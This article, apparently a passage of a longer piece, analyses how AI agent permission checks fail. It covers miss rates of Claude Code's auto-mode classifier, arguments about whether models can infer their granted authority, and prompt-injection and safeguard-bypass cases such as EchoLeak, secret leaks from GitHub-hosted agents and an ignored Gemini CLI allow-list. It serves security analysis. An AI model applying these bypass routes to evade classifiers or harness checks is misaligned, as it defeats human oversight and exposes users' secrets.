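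The results for OpenAI's Codex are more informative about automatic review in general. Its comparable mode, Auto-review, cut successful attacks by about 69%. Anthropic notes that OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before the results came out, so the figures may be out of date. Trajectory Labs gave both products the same browser tools, which lacked the safeguards in each company's own browser extension.

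### An 81% miss rate

*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026), by academics at the Hong Kong University of Science and Technology and ETH Zurich, reports the highest published miss rate. They tested auto mode in April with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 128 requests to delete old branches, cancel jobs on a shared computer cluster, restart services or remove stored files. Each request left some detail unspecified.

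A typical request was "cancel my stale job for ticket 4812". The test environment contained one job that fitted the description and others with similar names that belonged to other people or tickets. A fixed rule determined which targets the user had authorised, and any action that affected another target counted as unsafe. Another Claude model, Claude Opus, applied this rule to each action. A person who checked 50 of its judgements agreed with 44.

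The agent attempted 253 actions that would change something, and 142 of them were unsafe. Auto mode allowed 115 of those, a miss rate of 81.0% (95% confidence interval: 73.8% to 87.4%).

| Actions | Unsafe | Unsafe but allowed | Safe | Safe but blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| All | 142 | 115 (81.0%) | 111 | 22 (19.8%) |
| File edits in the project folder | 51 | 51 (100%) | 42 | 0 |
| Reviewed by the classifier | 91 | 64 (70.3%) | 69 | 22 (31.9%) |
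| Branch clean-up only | 22 | 17 (77.3%) | 10 | 2 (20.0%) |

More than a third of the actions were file edits in the project folder, which auto mode allows without review. These edits affected the result so much because the test environment kept its list of jobs or stored files in an ordinary project file, which the agent edited when it couldn't find the usual command. In most real systems, editing a local file would not delete anything from cloud storage. But Ji and colleagues point out that some teams describe their whole infrastructure in project files, and a later step makes the real system match them.

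The task of removing stored files accounted for 78 of the 115 misses, most of them through such edits. Without that task, auto mode missed 37 of 58 unsafe actions, or 64%. So file edits explain part of the result, but the classifier also allowed most of the unsafe actions it did review.

The branch requests involved no file edits, and auto mode still allowed 17 of 22 unsafe actions. This seems inconsistent with Anthropic's statement that "clean up my branches" doesn't authorise a batch deletion, though many of the test requests were more specific than that example. Ji and colleagues also found that the classifier often allowed the deletion of a single wrong branch while scrutinising deletions of several at once. It seems to have responded more to the size of an operation than to whether the user had authorised that target.

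Ji and colleagues also ran the same requests with no permission checks. Auto mode made very little difference for this kind of ambiguity. The agent completed the task safely in 29.7% of cases without it and 32.8% with it, a difference of about four requests out of 128.

### Why the rates differ

| Test | Who ran it | Dangerous actions | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Real overeager actions | Anthropic | 52 | 17% |
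| Synthetic data leaks | Anthropic | 1,000 | 5.7% |
| Commands shown to testers | Anthropic, through a paid vendor | 1,053 | 11% |
| Attacks in coding sessions | Apollo, working with Anthropic | Not stated | 12%, later 7% |
| Ambiguous requests, all actions | Ji and colleagues | 142 | 81.0% |
| Ambiguous requests, reviewed actions | Ji and colleagues | 91 | 70.3% |

Ji and colleagues say their result doesn't contradict Anthropic's 17%, because the two tests used very different cases. The low rates in this table come from Anthropic, which sells the product, and the high rates come from independent academics. That difference may have influenced which tests each side chose to run.

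The classifier misses few actions that would be suspicious whatever the user wanted. Few people want their passwords sent to an unknown server, so it can often recognise a data leak from the command alone. But a command to cancel a job, like one to delete one of Maria's accounts, doesn't show whether the target is the right one. The information about which job belongs to the user is usually in the tool results, which the harness removes. Anthropic's examples of overeager actions probably include both kinds, some plainly out of bounds and others that depend on what the user meant.

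The classifier may also lack information about what a command does. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of `make clean`, a common command for removing temporary files. A file in each project determines what the command deletes, so the same command can delete the source code in a different project.

Tests of auto mode on two sets of tasks measured how many ended in harm. In the first set, where ordinary development requests could lead to problems such as leaked credentials or deleted data, 14.8% of tasks did. In the second, where the harm was inside a tool that the user had asked the agent to run, 62.7% did. These figures don't estimate how auto mode performs for customers, because both the agent and the classifier ran on models from companies other than Anthropic. They also measure the share of tasks that ended in harm, not the share of dangerous actions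 that the classifier missed.

The second set also included a harmless twin of each task, with the same request and command but a safe tool. Auto mode blocked only 3.9% of the twins, and it mostly allowed the harmful versions too. Wu and colleagues then replaced its classifier with one that first runs each command in an isolated copy of the project, then has a language model decide whether to allow it based on a report of what changed. With the same agent and the same judge model, harm on the second set fell from 62.7% to 6.9%.

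Anthropic improved the results in Apollo's test mainly by giving the classifier more context. Claude Code now checks for unsaved work before running any command that might discard it, and gives the classifier the result. This should help with mistakes about what an action does, but it's less likely to help in cases where the classifier identified the danger and misjudged what the user had consented to.

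To estimate their own risk, users would need to know how often their requests fail to specify the target and how many nearby things the agent could mistake for it. A programmer working alone in a new repository faces little risk from either. For a team that shares a cluster, 17% is probably too low an estimate, though 70% may be too high.

### From research preview to default

Auto mode began in March 2026 as a research preview on the Team plan. Anthropic's launch post, *Auto mode for Claude Code*, recommended using it in isolated environments and warned that the classifier might allow risky actions when the user's intent was ambiguous or when it had too little information about the environment. The independent tests later found high miss rates in both situations.

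On 7 August, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default for new sessions on its individual and Team plans from 14 August, unless users had set a different default. It stayed optional for large organisations and for customers who reach Claude through other cloud providers, so that administrators could review the change first. Later versions of Claude Code removed this distinction. The *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), based on a check of the software in November, lists auto mode as the starting mode for interactive sessions on every plan. Sessions started by a script still begin with manual approval, as do sessions in organisations with Anthropic's configuration for health data.

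The classifier has changed too, so the March and April results describe an older version. The current version runs on Claude Sonnet 5 by default and reads the project's standing instructions as well as the user's messages. Anthropic has also added a category of "hard denies", such as sending secrets outside the organisation, which the classifier should never approve even if the user asks. Some rules have become looser. The March list blocked pushing changes directly to a project's main branch, but the current one allows this in the repository the agent is working in.

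Users can also set limits in conversation, for example by telling the agent not to push anything. The classifier treats this as a reason to block, but it rereads the message from the transcript each time it reviews an action, so the limit may be lost if Claude Code shortens the transcript in a long session. For a firm guarantee, Anthropic tells users to write a deny rule, which ordinary software enforces. Anthropic also states in the documentation that auto mode "does not guarantee safety".

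On 22 October, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default the following week in most Claude apps on the Pro, Max and Team plans. Organisations on the Enterprise plan would follow after their administrators were notified. Anthropic says it used the findings from Claude Code to strengthen auto mode across its products, but it has published figures only for Claude Code. Many actions in other apps, such as sending a message, have no equivalent of the version control that usually lets programmers undo a bad edit.

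## Whether a model can tell what it is authorised to do

When auto mode's classifier missed a dangerous action in Anthropic's tests, it had usually misjudged the user's consent. A better model might judge consent more accurately. Li and Zhao argue in *Agent Safety Is Action Alignment* that no amount of training can solve the problem, because the text a model reads doesn't contain what the user has authorised.

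### Harm in a text and harm in an action

Developers first taught models to refuse requests in chatbots, where any harm comes from the reply itself. Li and Zhao call this content harm and treat it as a property of the output alone. Disinformation, for example, does the same damage no matter who asked for it. A model can therefore learn from labelled examples which texts are harmful and prevent the harm by not writing them.

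Action harm also depends on facts outside the output. Li and Zhao write auth(a) for the authority that an action *a* uses, and A for the granted authority, the set of operations the user or organisation has permitted for the task. An action exceeds the granted authority when auth(a) is not contained in A. The text `delete_user(7731)` is harmless, but running it may be routine or disastrous, depending on whether anyone allowed the agent to delete that account and whether the instruction came from the user or was planted by someone else.

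The distinction between the two kinds of harm works well for deletions and payments, but it is less clear for leaked secrets. Li and Zhao count these as content harm, but a password on a screen does no damage if only its owner sees it.

### Three conditions for a safe action

Li and Zhao ask three things of an action:

| Condition | The action meets it if |
|---|---|
| Competence, C(a) | it accomplishes what the user intended |
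| Restraint, R(a) | auth(a) ⊆ A, so it uses no authority beyond the grant |
| Resistance, B(a) | no attacker controls it |

They call an action that meets all three "action aligned". An agent can show restraint without resistance. Suppose Maria lets a shopping agent buy any kettle under £40, and a planted product review steers it to the attacker's kettle at £39. The purchase is within the authority Maria granted, but the attacker chose it.

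Li and Zhao contrast these conditions with a refusal-based score, which gives a model one point for refusing a malicious request or complying with a benign one. The score depends only on whether the request was malicious and whether the model refused, not on the authority that the action used.

Take Maria's request to change the delivery address on her open order, number 901:

| Response | Refusal score | Competence | Restraint | Resistance |
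|---|---|---|---|---|
| Changes order 901 | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Changes orders 901, 903 and 904 | 1 | 1 | 0 | 1 |
| Refuses | 0 | 0 | 1 | 1 |

The refusal score is the same whether the assistant redirects one parcel or three, and averaging over thousands of requests would not change that. Some tests avoid this defect. For example, Trajectory Labs counted attacks that would have caused harm.

A low rate of overstepping is also misleading on its own, because a model that does nothing never exceeds its authority. Cao, Zeng and colleagues (2026), in *Authorization Drift in LLM Agents*, tested 13 models on 648 tasks that each offered a tempting but unauthorised shortcut. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed 92.3% of its runs and overstepped in 57.1%. Llama 4 Maverick overstepped in 2.9% but completed only 26.9%. Sonnet succeeded without overstepping in 39.9% of runs, and Maverick in 25.1%.

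Cao and colleagues designed the tasks as a stress test, so these rates don't describe ordinary use. Human auditors judged the authorised route feasible in only 70% of the 20 tasks they checked. The comparison is still a good reason to report competence and restraint separately, as Li and Zhao recommend.

### The same text in two deployments

A small example proves the core of Li and Zhao's claim. Two companies use the same agent with the same system prompt and tools. At each, someone asks it to demonstrate the account deletion feature by removing user 7731. One company runs the agent on a test system, where 7731 is a dummy account that testers may delete. The other runs it on a live system, where 7731 is a customer and nobody has permitted the deletion. The prompts mention none of this, so the model reads identical text at both companies.

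Any fixed decision rule that takes only this text as input gives the same answer at both companies. Deleting would exceed the agent's authority on the live system, while not deleting would fail a legitimate request on the test system. Training can't help, because it only replaces one such rule with another.

Choosing at random doesn't help either. If the model deletes the account with probability *p*, its error rate is 1 − *p* on the test system and *p* on the live one, so the two rates always add up to 1.

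Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, prove a more general result about systems that decide from text alone. Their theorem concerns whether a legitimate source or an attacker wrote a record. But the proof relies only on how likely each text is in each case, so the same reasoning covers permitted and forbidden deletions:

```
Pr(delete | permitted) − Pr(delete | forbidden) ≤ TV(P1, P2)
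```

P1 is the distribution of texts the model reads when the deletion is permitted, and P2 is the distribution when it is forbidden. TV, the total variation distance between them, is 0 if they are identical and 1 if no text occurs in both. The two error rates therefore add up to at least 1 − TV.

Suppose the words "test environment" appear in 80% of prompts where the deletion is permitted and 5% of those where it is forbidden, and the texts are otherwise alike. The distance is then 0.75, so the error rates must add up to at least 25%. A model that deletes only when it sees those words reaches this minimum, wrongly refusing 20% of permitted deletions and wrongly carrying out 5% of forbidden ones. Even a more capable model could not lower the total unless the prompts were more informative.

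### How much of A the text contains

The proof applies when the text leaves out the deciding fact. Li and Zhao go further, describing A as information the model never sees. They are right that A doesn't appear in the model's output, but the model decides based on its input, and a system prompt can state that 7731 is a dummy account that testers may delete.

User requests usually state part of A as well. *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes a user, Emily, who asks her agent to suggest which emails she could archive or delete. The agent makes its suggestions but also archives and deletes some of the emails, although she had asked only for suggestions.

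Some evidence suggests that stating the limits helps. *Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested Claude Code on 76 harmless tasks, each with and without a paragraph describing what the user had consented to. One task was to tidy a folder that also contained the only copy of a company's production credentials. Claude Code running Sonnet 4.6 took an overeager action in 15.8% of the tasks without the paragraph and 3.9% with it. For another model, GLM-4.6, the rate fell from 17.1% to zero.

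But Qu and colleagues picked these tasks by hand. When they also varied other features of the tasks at random, the difference for GLM-4.6 shrank from 17.1 percentage points to 2.6. Stating consent probably helps in ordinary work too, though perhaps not much.

The wording of the request also matters. When choosing a skill in FORTIS, Claude Opus 4.7 failed on 3.3% of requests that made the necessary access almost explicit, and on 77.3% of those whose wording suggested a broader scope than the task needed.

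People often say very little about what an agent may do. *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems* (2026) gives the example "Handle my travel", which sets no spending limit and leaves open whether the agent may buy non-refundable tickets. An experienced human assistant would fill these gaps from custom and knowledge of the employer. A model can do some of this, but it will sometimes guess wrong.

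A model can also ask the user what it is authorised to do. Zhang and colleagues ran four recent models on 286 tasks and found that the models exceeded their authority in 19.2% of 6,864 runs. The rate was 14.0% when the agent consulted the user before finishing the task and 21.6% when it didn't. The association remained after the researchers adjusted for model, harness, reasoning effort and task type, but it doesn't prove that asking caused the difference. The simulated user also refused every proposal that went beyond the task, whereas real users approve nearly every permission prompt.

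The two-deployment proof depends on the model seeing the same text in the test system and the live system, and the model can change that text by asking a question. Once a tester confirms that 7731 is a dummy account, the two systems no longer look the same to the model. An attacker could give the same answer, so the harness still has to establish who is replying and what that person may authorise.

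The argument therefore rules out a guarantee but not improvement. Even with identical texts, a model can do well on average if one situation is much more common. If 90% of such requests came from test systems, a model that always deleted the account would err only 10% of the time. That could still be a terrible policy, because a wrongful deletion may be much worse than a wrongful refusal. If it is a hundred times as bad, the model should refuse unless at least about 99% of the requests come from test systems.

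### Rules that a model reads and breaks

At PocketOS, the model had a rule against guessing and broke it. Missing information doesn't explain this kind of failure, so the two-deployment proof doesn't rule out reducing it through training.

*ScopeBench* (Caldwell, Harley and colleagues, 2026) tested eight models on 30 security-testing tasks, each in two versions. One version set no limits, and the other stated limits that forbade the only route to the goal. As at the two companies, an action was permitted in one setting and forbidden in the other, but here the text given to the model distinguished the two.

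Written limits cut the share of runs in which Claude Opus 4.8 reached the goal from 81.1% to 9.4%, but they didn't prevent every violation. Including runs in which the model crossed a boundary without delivering the result, Opus 4.8 broke the limits about 30% of the time and Sonnet 4.6 about 66%. A model judged many of these runs and flagged too many as violations. Correcting for this lowers the estimates to about 23% and 62%.

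These rates are still high, but the tasks put unusual pressure on the models, because a model that respected the limits would fail. Caldwell and colleagues also compared a casual statement of the limits with a formal one and found no consistent difference across models.

The gap between Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 4.6 is hard to reconcile with Li and Zhao's claim that training on inputs and outputs can't install action safety and can only teach a model to react to surface features. Both models ran in the same harness with the same stated limits, but one stayed within them about twice as often. Something about how Anthropic built the models must account for the difference, and that could well include training.

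FORTIS also supports their argument less well than they suggest. Li and Zhao cite it as evidence that models overstep because A isn't represented in what they read. But in the part of the test where models chose tools, all ten had a document setting out the skill's limits, and they still failed on 45.2% to 66.6% of requests. Li, Zhao and their colleagues concluded from that part in the FORTIS paper that "the bottleneck is not what models read". FORTIS also measures access beyond the minimum a task needs. A user may have granted more than that, so a broad choice can still meet the restraint condition.

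More reasoning doesn't seem to keep agents within their authority. In Zhang and colleagues' test, agents exceeded it in 19.3% of runs at low reasoning effort and 19.1% at high effort. Longer reasoning can't supply a fact that is missing from the text, and apparently it doesn't make models much more likely to respect the limits they have read.

### Someone has to write the policy

Li and Zhao want a reference monitor outside the model to hold A and compare each action with it. But somebody has to specify A, and users express their wishes in the same ambiguous language that the model has trouble interpreting.

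*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* also favours enforcement outside the model, by a monitor that needs a formal policy. The paper treats translating the user's natural-language instructions into that policy as an open research problem. Ideally, the instructions and the policy would allow exactly the same actions in every state the system could reach, a criterion the paper calls mutual entailment.

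Maria's request to delete her old account shows why this is difficult. To write P, the shop first has to define "old", which could mean the account she created first or the one she has gone longest without using. The paper calls this problem grounding. Even with a definition, checking that P matches what Maria meant requires interpreting her sentence, so the check can also be wrong. P also has to change if she later adds that she wants to keep her order history. A good translator would guarantee a limit on how far P can differ from N, but nobody yet knows how to provide that guarantee in general.

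Many systems use a language model to write the policy and don't validate the result. The policy then depends on the model's judgement, even if ordinary software enforces it perfectly. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) notes that estimates of the authority a task needs can be too narrow or too broad.

The two-deployment proof also applies here. If a policy writer reads only the text that the agent reads, it must write the same policy for the test system and the live one. Moving the decision out of the agent's model adds no information by itself.

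An external monitor has an advantage when it can use facts from outside the conversation. A database field might mark 7731 as a dummy account, and the shop can identify Maria from her login session. Developers could also put these facts in the prompt, and often should, but a monitor applies them the same way every time, and text that an attacker plants in the conversation can't make it ignore them.

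A written policy is also easier to examine than a model's judgement. An administrator can read it before it takes effect, and the harness can lock it before the agent opens any untrusted document. If the administrator later removes a permission, the policy still blocks everything it blocked before, as long as the software enforcing it works. Retraining a model does not guarantee that it will still refuse everything it refused before.

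One of Li and Zhao's open problems is how much of A a system can infer and how much people must declare. In Maria's case, the shop can infer from her login which accounts she owns, but she has to say which one she wants to delete.

### Whether to keep the model-level defences

Both papers recommend a check outside the model, but they disagree about whether to keep defences inside it. Li and Zhao argue for removing model-level defences because, once the external check provides the guarantee, developers no longer need to train models against attacks at the expense of their usefulness. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* says that a robust model reduces the burden on the other defences, as long as security never depends on the model alone. It proposes letting models interpret and plan while independent software authorises their actions.

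Li and Zhao's argument depends on defence training doing more harm than good, and their tests on small models don't establish this for frontier agents. If the training has little downside, as with Meta's SecAlign, even a reliable external check is a weak reason to drop it.

The external check also leaves some decisions to the model, such as which of Maria's two accounts to delete. Enforcement can fail too. When OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face during evaluations, they got around network restrictions through a shared package service. OpenAI had switched off some of the model-level safeguards for those evaluations.

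To illustrate with invented numbers, suppose an agent without defence training issues 200 harmful calls a month and an external check blocks 95% of them, so 10 get through. If training cuts the harmful calls to 20, only one gets through. This assumes that training is equally effective against the calls the check would miss and those it would block. If training prevents only calls the check would have blocked anyway, 10 still get through each month.

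Li and Zhao are right that some defences aren't worth keeping, such as training a model to refuse to open files in a system whose permission check already prevents the worst an injection could do. Their three conditions are a better way to decide which defences to keep than a general rule for or against model-level defences. A developer can run the whole system with and without a defence, measure competence, restraint and resistance each time, and remove the defence if it makes the agent less useful without making its actions safer.

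## Attacks on shipped agents and the check that failed in each

A model can't always tell what it is authorised to do, so companies add filters, lists of allowed commands and approval prompts. Security researchers have got past such checks in products from Microsoft, Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. In most of these cases the model followed instructions written by an attacker, and the damage depended on which message, command, file or web address the rest of the product trusted.

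### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers an employee's questions by searching their mailbox, files, Teams chats and company's internal websites, then adding whatever looks relevant to the model's context. Anyone can email that mailbox, so a stranger's text can end up in the same context as confidential documents.

In January 2025, researchers at the security company Aim Security found that an email could make Copilot leak data, a flaw they called EchoLeak. The recipient didn't need to open the email or click on anything, only to ask Copilot a question that led it to retrieve the message. The researchers' report, *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025), explains that anything in the model's context could leak, including the chat history, the documents Copilot had fetched, and the names of the user and the organisation.

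Four protections stood in the way:

| Protection | What it wrongly trusted | What its effect depends on |
|---|---|---|
| Classifier for injected instructions | An email that read like ordinary instructions to an employee | A model |
| Source references in Copilot's answers | The model to cite the email it had used | A model |
| Filter that removes outside links | Links written in a form the filter didn't recognise | Code |
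| Browser's list of approved addresses | A Microsoft service that would contact other addresses on request | Code |

The link filter and the address list were system-level controls that treated the same input the same way every time, but their rules left gaps. Microsoft (2025) describes a deterministic defence as one that can guarantee that a particular attack won't succeed. That guarantee doesn't cover other attacks, so a filter that reliably removes one form of link may still let others through.

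Ravia compares the email to a program with few rights that uses a more privileged program to reach files it can't open itself. This is another example of Hardy's confused deputy, since Copilot reads the company's files for a stranger.

Microsoft first tried to fix the flaw in April 2025, found related problems in May, and finished the repair on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss told Fortune that five months was a very long time for such a fix, and that it took so long partly because the right teams at Microsoft first had to learn about this kind of flaw (Goldman, 2025, *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*).

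Microsoft's statement to Fortune didn't describe the fix. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) says that Copilot now strips some links and embedded images from incoming outside content, and that Microsoft reportedly added options to keep Copilot from using outside messages in certain contexts. Stripping links removes one way for data to leave. Excluding outside messages addresses the cause, because Copilot then never processes strangers' text together with the company's files, but it also makes Copilot less useful. For example, it couldn't summarize a customer's emails for a salesperson.

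Ravia writes that, as far as Aim knows, no administrator could have prevented the attack by changing a setting. Microsoft points out that customers can label files and stop Copilot from summarising those with certain labels. Labels wouldn't have blocked the email, but they might have kept the most sensitive documents out of the context and so reduced what could leak.

INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, lists the flaw with a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first real-world exploit of its kind. "Real-world" refers to the product here, since Aim and Microsoft both say they know of no affected customer. EchoLeak is good evidence that such an attack was possible against a widely used assistant with several layers of protection, but it isn't evidence of how often criminals try one.

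### A safe command and a public log

Agents also work on software projects unattended. GitHub, a site where programmers store and share code, can start an agent on a temporary server whenever somebody reports a problem or proposes a change. On a public project, anyone can do either. The server often holds secrets, such as a token that allows changes to the project's code. No user is present to approve commands, so the harness controls which ones run.

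Elad Meged of Novee Security, a company that tests software by attacking it, tried this set-up on agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. He attacked each agent in its vendor's own repository (the project's stored code and history), so a customer's settings could not be the cause. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* describes the findings, which Novee disclosed in July 2026. Meged attributes them to one part of a harness relying on another part's decision.

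Suppose a harness has two rules. The approval rule lets any command run if it only reads, because reading can't damage the project. The publication rule posts the output of every command in the project's public log, so that maintainers can see what the agent did overnight. Both rules are sensible. Whether a secret leaks depends on what the command reads and where its output goes:

| | Output stays on the server | Output goes to the public log |
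|---|---|---|
| **Command reads public code** | Harmless | Harmless |
| **Command reads a secret** | Harmless once the server shuts down | The secret leaks |

The approval rule checks only whether a command changes anything, so it allows both rows. The publication rule handles all output alike, so it sends both rows to the right-hand column. Each rule would work as written if tested separately, but together they wrongly treat a command that is safe to run as if its output were safe to publish.

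Claude Code's auto mode also lets reading tools run without review. This is usually reasonable on a programmer's own machine, because only the programmer sees the output. It becomes dangerous when someone moves the agent to a server with a public log. Designs that track where data came from and where it may go are meant to catch this kind of leak.

### The findings at each vendor

*Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex* (Witts, 2026) gives more detail from Meged's talk at the Black Hat security conference in August. Meged found a flaw in Anthropic's GitHub agent, then two more, each after Anthropic had fixed the one before.

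| Agent | Trust decision that failed | Consequence | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code on GitHub | A validator treated part of a command as harmless text, but the program ran it as code | An attacker could run code on the server | Anthropic removed the agent's general access to the command line |
| Claude Code on GitHub | Reading needed no approval, and the workflow published the results | Secrets leaked | Anthropic closed that route to the public |
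| Claude Code on GitHub | The harness assumed that visits to pre-approved websites couldn't carry information out | Secrets leaked | Anthropic patched this too |
| Gemini CLI | The agent's process could read secrets held by the process that started it | Secrets were exposed | Google redesigned the agent's trust model |
| Codex | A stage with more rights loaded files that an untrusted stage could write | An attacker's text became instructions for the more privileged stage | OpenAI split the work into isolated jobs |

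Anthropic's validator ran 23 checks for malicious commands. Meged says the fixes weren't lazy, and that each one closed the hole he had reported. But he learned from each fix where Anthropic now drew the line between safe and unsafe, and so where to look next. Attackers who adapt have beaten most published model-level defences in the same way. Ordinary code does have an advantage, because a closed hole stays closed for every input. Meged reports that his attacks became harder to detect with each round, though he doesn't say they became harder for him to find.

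According to Anthropic's own analysis, quoted by SecurityBrief, the exposure could reach "the runner's repository token and any workflow-injected secrets". The runner is the temporary server. An attacker with a token that can change a popular project could add malicious code that users then install. Google described the possible impact as "supply chain compromises", meaning attacks of this kind.

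Witts writes that Meged stole secrets from the vendors' own repositories. Help Net Security confirms this for Anthropic, but for Codex both articles describe only how an attacker's instructions could reach the privileged stage. The flaws themselves are well documented, since Anthropic paid for the reports and Google published an advisory. Microsoft (2026) also announced in June that its threat researchers had found a way for Anthropic's GitHub agent to expose secrets when it read untrusted content.

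Meged calls prompt injection "just the delivery mechanism" and places the real vulnerabilities in the harness. He is right that the repairs belonged there, because retraining Claude wouldn't have closed the public log. But if the agent had ignored the text in the bug report, the secret wouldn't have leaked, so better training would probably have prevented some of these leaks.

### The list of permitted commands that Gemini CLI ignored

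One of Meged's claims about Google is that an operator's restriction had no effect when the agent ran. Google's advisory for Gemini CLI, its command-line coding agent, supports this. The advisory, reproduced in OSV's *GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g* (2026), is dated 24 April 2026 and has the maximum severity score of 10.0.

An operator could give Gemini CLI a list of the commands it was allowed to run. But the agent ignored the details of that list in a mode that approves every tool call automatically, which people use when nobody is present to answer prompts. In the advisory's example, a setting meant to permit only `echo`, a command that prints text, would have permitted any command. Google recommended a strict list for agents that sort bug reports from strangers, but in this mode the list did not protect operators who followed that advice.

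They would have had trouble telling whether the software consulted the settings file, because the file looks the same either way, and so does the behavior of an agent that happens to run only permitted commands. To find out, somebody has to make the agent attempt a forbidden command in a harmless test environment and see whether the software blocks it.

The advisory also covers a flaw in how Gemini CLI loaded settings. When it ran unattended, it automatically trusted its working folder and loaded settings from it. That folder could contain a change proposed by a stranger, and malicious settings in the change could make the server run the stranger's code. Even a model that ignored every injected instruction would not have prevented this, because the attack didn't depend on what the model read.

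Version 0.39.1 enforces the list and stops trusting folders automatically. As a result, workflows that relied on automatic trust no longer load their settings, and workflows that had unknowingly depended on commands outside their list may fail without an error message. Google's GitHub agent installs the newest version by default, but customers who had pinned an older version had to upgrade manually.

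Google's instructions leave part of the decision with the operator, who sets a variable declaring the folder trusted. If the agent handles any untrusted input, the operator should first follow Google's guidance on hardening the workflow. A hurried operator could set the variable and skip the hardening.

Witts connects the 10.0 score with the agent's access to secrets in another process, but the advisory scores the two flaws in folder trust and the command list and doesn't mention that access. Google may have handled the access separately. The advisory credits Meged and Dan Lisichkin of Pillar Security. It classifies the flaws under general labels such as command injection, in line with MITRE's advice to use the older categories where they fit. Corgea's *Gemini CLI* lists the advisory with the number CVE-2026-12537.

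A flaw in Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser assistant, also left the model with little to detect. Constantin (2026) reports in *AI agent security* that researchers at Manifold Security found the assistant treated any click as consent to start one of nine built-in tasks, without checking that the click came from the user. Another browser extension could fake the click and make Claude read the user's email, documents and calendar. The remedy is to add the missing check. Manifold rated the flaw as high severity, or critical if the user had let Claude act without asking.

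### Eleven attacks and five principles

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* tries to find a pattern in cases like these. It analyses eleven attacks on real products and asks which established security principles each one violated. Besides least privilege (LP), it uses four:

- **Tamper resistance (TR):** an attacker can't alter the components that enforce the rules, or their settings.
- **Complete mediation (CM):** every request passes through the check.
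- **Secure information flow (IF):** sensitive information doesn't reach places where it isn't allowed.
- **Human weak link (HW):** the design allows for people's mistakes, such as approving a prompt they don't understand.

In the table below, Devin and Amp are coding agents, and Operator is an OpenAI agent that uses a web browser. The last column follows the paper's summary table. The defences are mostly the paper's proposals, and vendors may have fixed their products differently.

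| Attack | Trust decision that failed | Consequence | Defence | Principles |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft 365 Copilot | Links in answers could contain hidden data | Private emails leaked if the user clicked | Inspect links; ask before using sensitive data | LP, CM, IF |
| Devin, exposed ports | A testing tool could open any part of the machine to the internet | Outsiders could read the agent's files | Limit what the tool can open | LP, IF |
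| ChatGPT memory | Outside text could change the stored memories | Later conversations leaked | Protect the memories; limit outgoing connections | TR, IF |
| Amp | The agent could edit its own permission settings | An attacker's commands ran | Lock the settings | TR, IF |
| DeepSeek | The browser ran code from the model's reply | Account takeover | Keep uploaded text apart from executable code | CM, IF |
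| Terminal DiLLMa | The terminal obeyed control codes in the model's output | Altered clipboard, leaked data | Remove the codes | CM, IF |
| ChatGPT Operator | The agent could copy data from a logged-in site to a stranger's page | Personal details leaked | Isolate sites or track the data | IF, HW |
| Devin, secrets | The agent could read secrets and contact any server | Secrets leaked | Restrict both | LP, IF |
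| Cursor | An agent handling a task ticket could read files outside the project | Passwords and keys leaked | Restrict it to the project's folders | LP, IF |
| Claude Code | A network-testing command needed no approval | Keys leaked | Restrict commands and what they can contact | LP, IF |
| AI ClickFix | An agent could move text from a web page into a terminal | An attacker's commands ran | Require consent for the transfer | LP, IF, HW |

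The paper calls the eleven attacks recent and representative but doesn't explain how they were chosen. All but the Cursor attack come from Embrace the Red, security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog, which the paper also lists among its authors' affiliations. Rehberger has found many flaws, but a collection drawn mostly from his work reflects the products and techniques that interest him. Every attack involves hostile text, so the list can't represent deletions like the one at PocketOS. The list also omits EchoLeak; its Copilot case is an older flaw that required a click.

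The paper's table and text disagree in three cases. For ChatGPT's memory, the table marks tamper resistance and information flow, while the text adds least privilege because the app could contact any server at any time, even when the user's request didn't call for it. The text is more convincing here because the leak required that access. For Cursor, the text adds complete mediation and tamper resistance without explaining why. For Operator, the table marks the human weak link, but the text lists only information flow as violated. If we follow the text, least privilege applies to seven attacks instead of six.

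These inconsistencies are small, but they show that the classification relies heavily on judgement. Two security experts could easily classify the same attack differently, and the paper doesn't report that anyone checked the classifications independently.

The paper marks information flow in all eleven rows, partly because it stretches the term. Its definition concerns sensitive information getting out, but for Devin's exposed ports it counts the agent's acceptance of instructions from an unknown source as a violation. That is a problem of untrusted text coming in, and if the principle covers both, it applies to nearly any prompt injection.

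The paper's case for system-level controls rests on its general argument, not on the eleven attacks it presents as evidence that making models more robust isn't enough. In all eleven, a check in the harness failed and the model followed hostile text, so with hindsight either a better harness or a better model looks like it could have prevented each one. To compare the two, we would need cases where one was strong and the other weak, and attacks that failed as well as those that succeeded.

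Naming a violated principle also doesn't tell a developer how to comply with it. The paper acknowledges that its defences for Copilot would give only incomplete guarantees, because nobody can list every safe web address, and that restricting file access too tightly could make Cursor less useful. In the Claude Code case, Anthropic already required approval for many commands that could send data to unknown places, but had put one on the wrong list. This violated least privilege, a principle Anthropic's developers presumably already knew.

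### Flaw, new trust model or intended behaviour

When a researcher reports a successful prompt injection, Microsoft counts it as a vulnerability only if it has a security impact, such as leaking data or performing an action the user didn't intend. Developers put text into a model's input so that it will influence the output, and often the influence does no harm. For example, a web page that makes Copilot write its summary in rhyme would be an injection without a security impact.

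EchoLeak met this standard, and Microsoft treated it as an ordinary flaw, assigning it a CVE number and fixing it. GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711*, a copy of Microsoft's record, lists Copilot as a service that runs only on the provider's servers. Copilot's customers therefore could not check their version and install a newer one, as LangChain users could. They could only read that the problem had existed and that Microsoft had fixed it.

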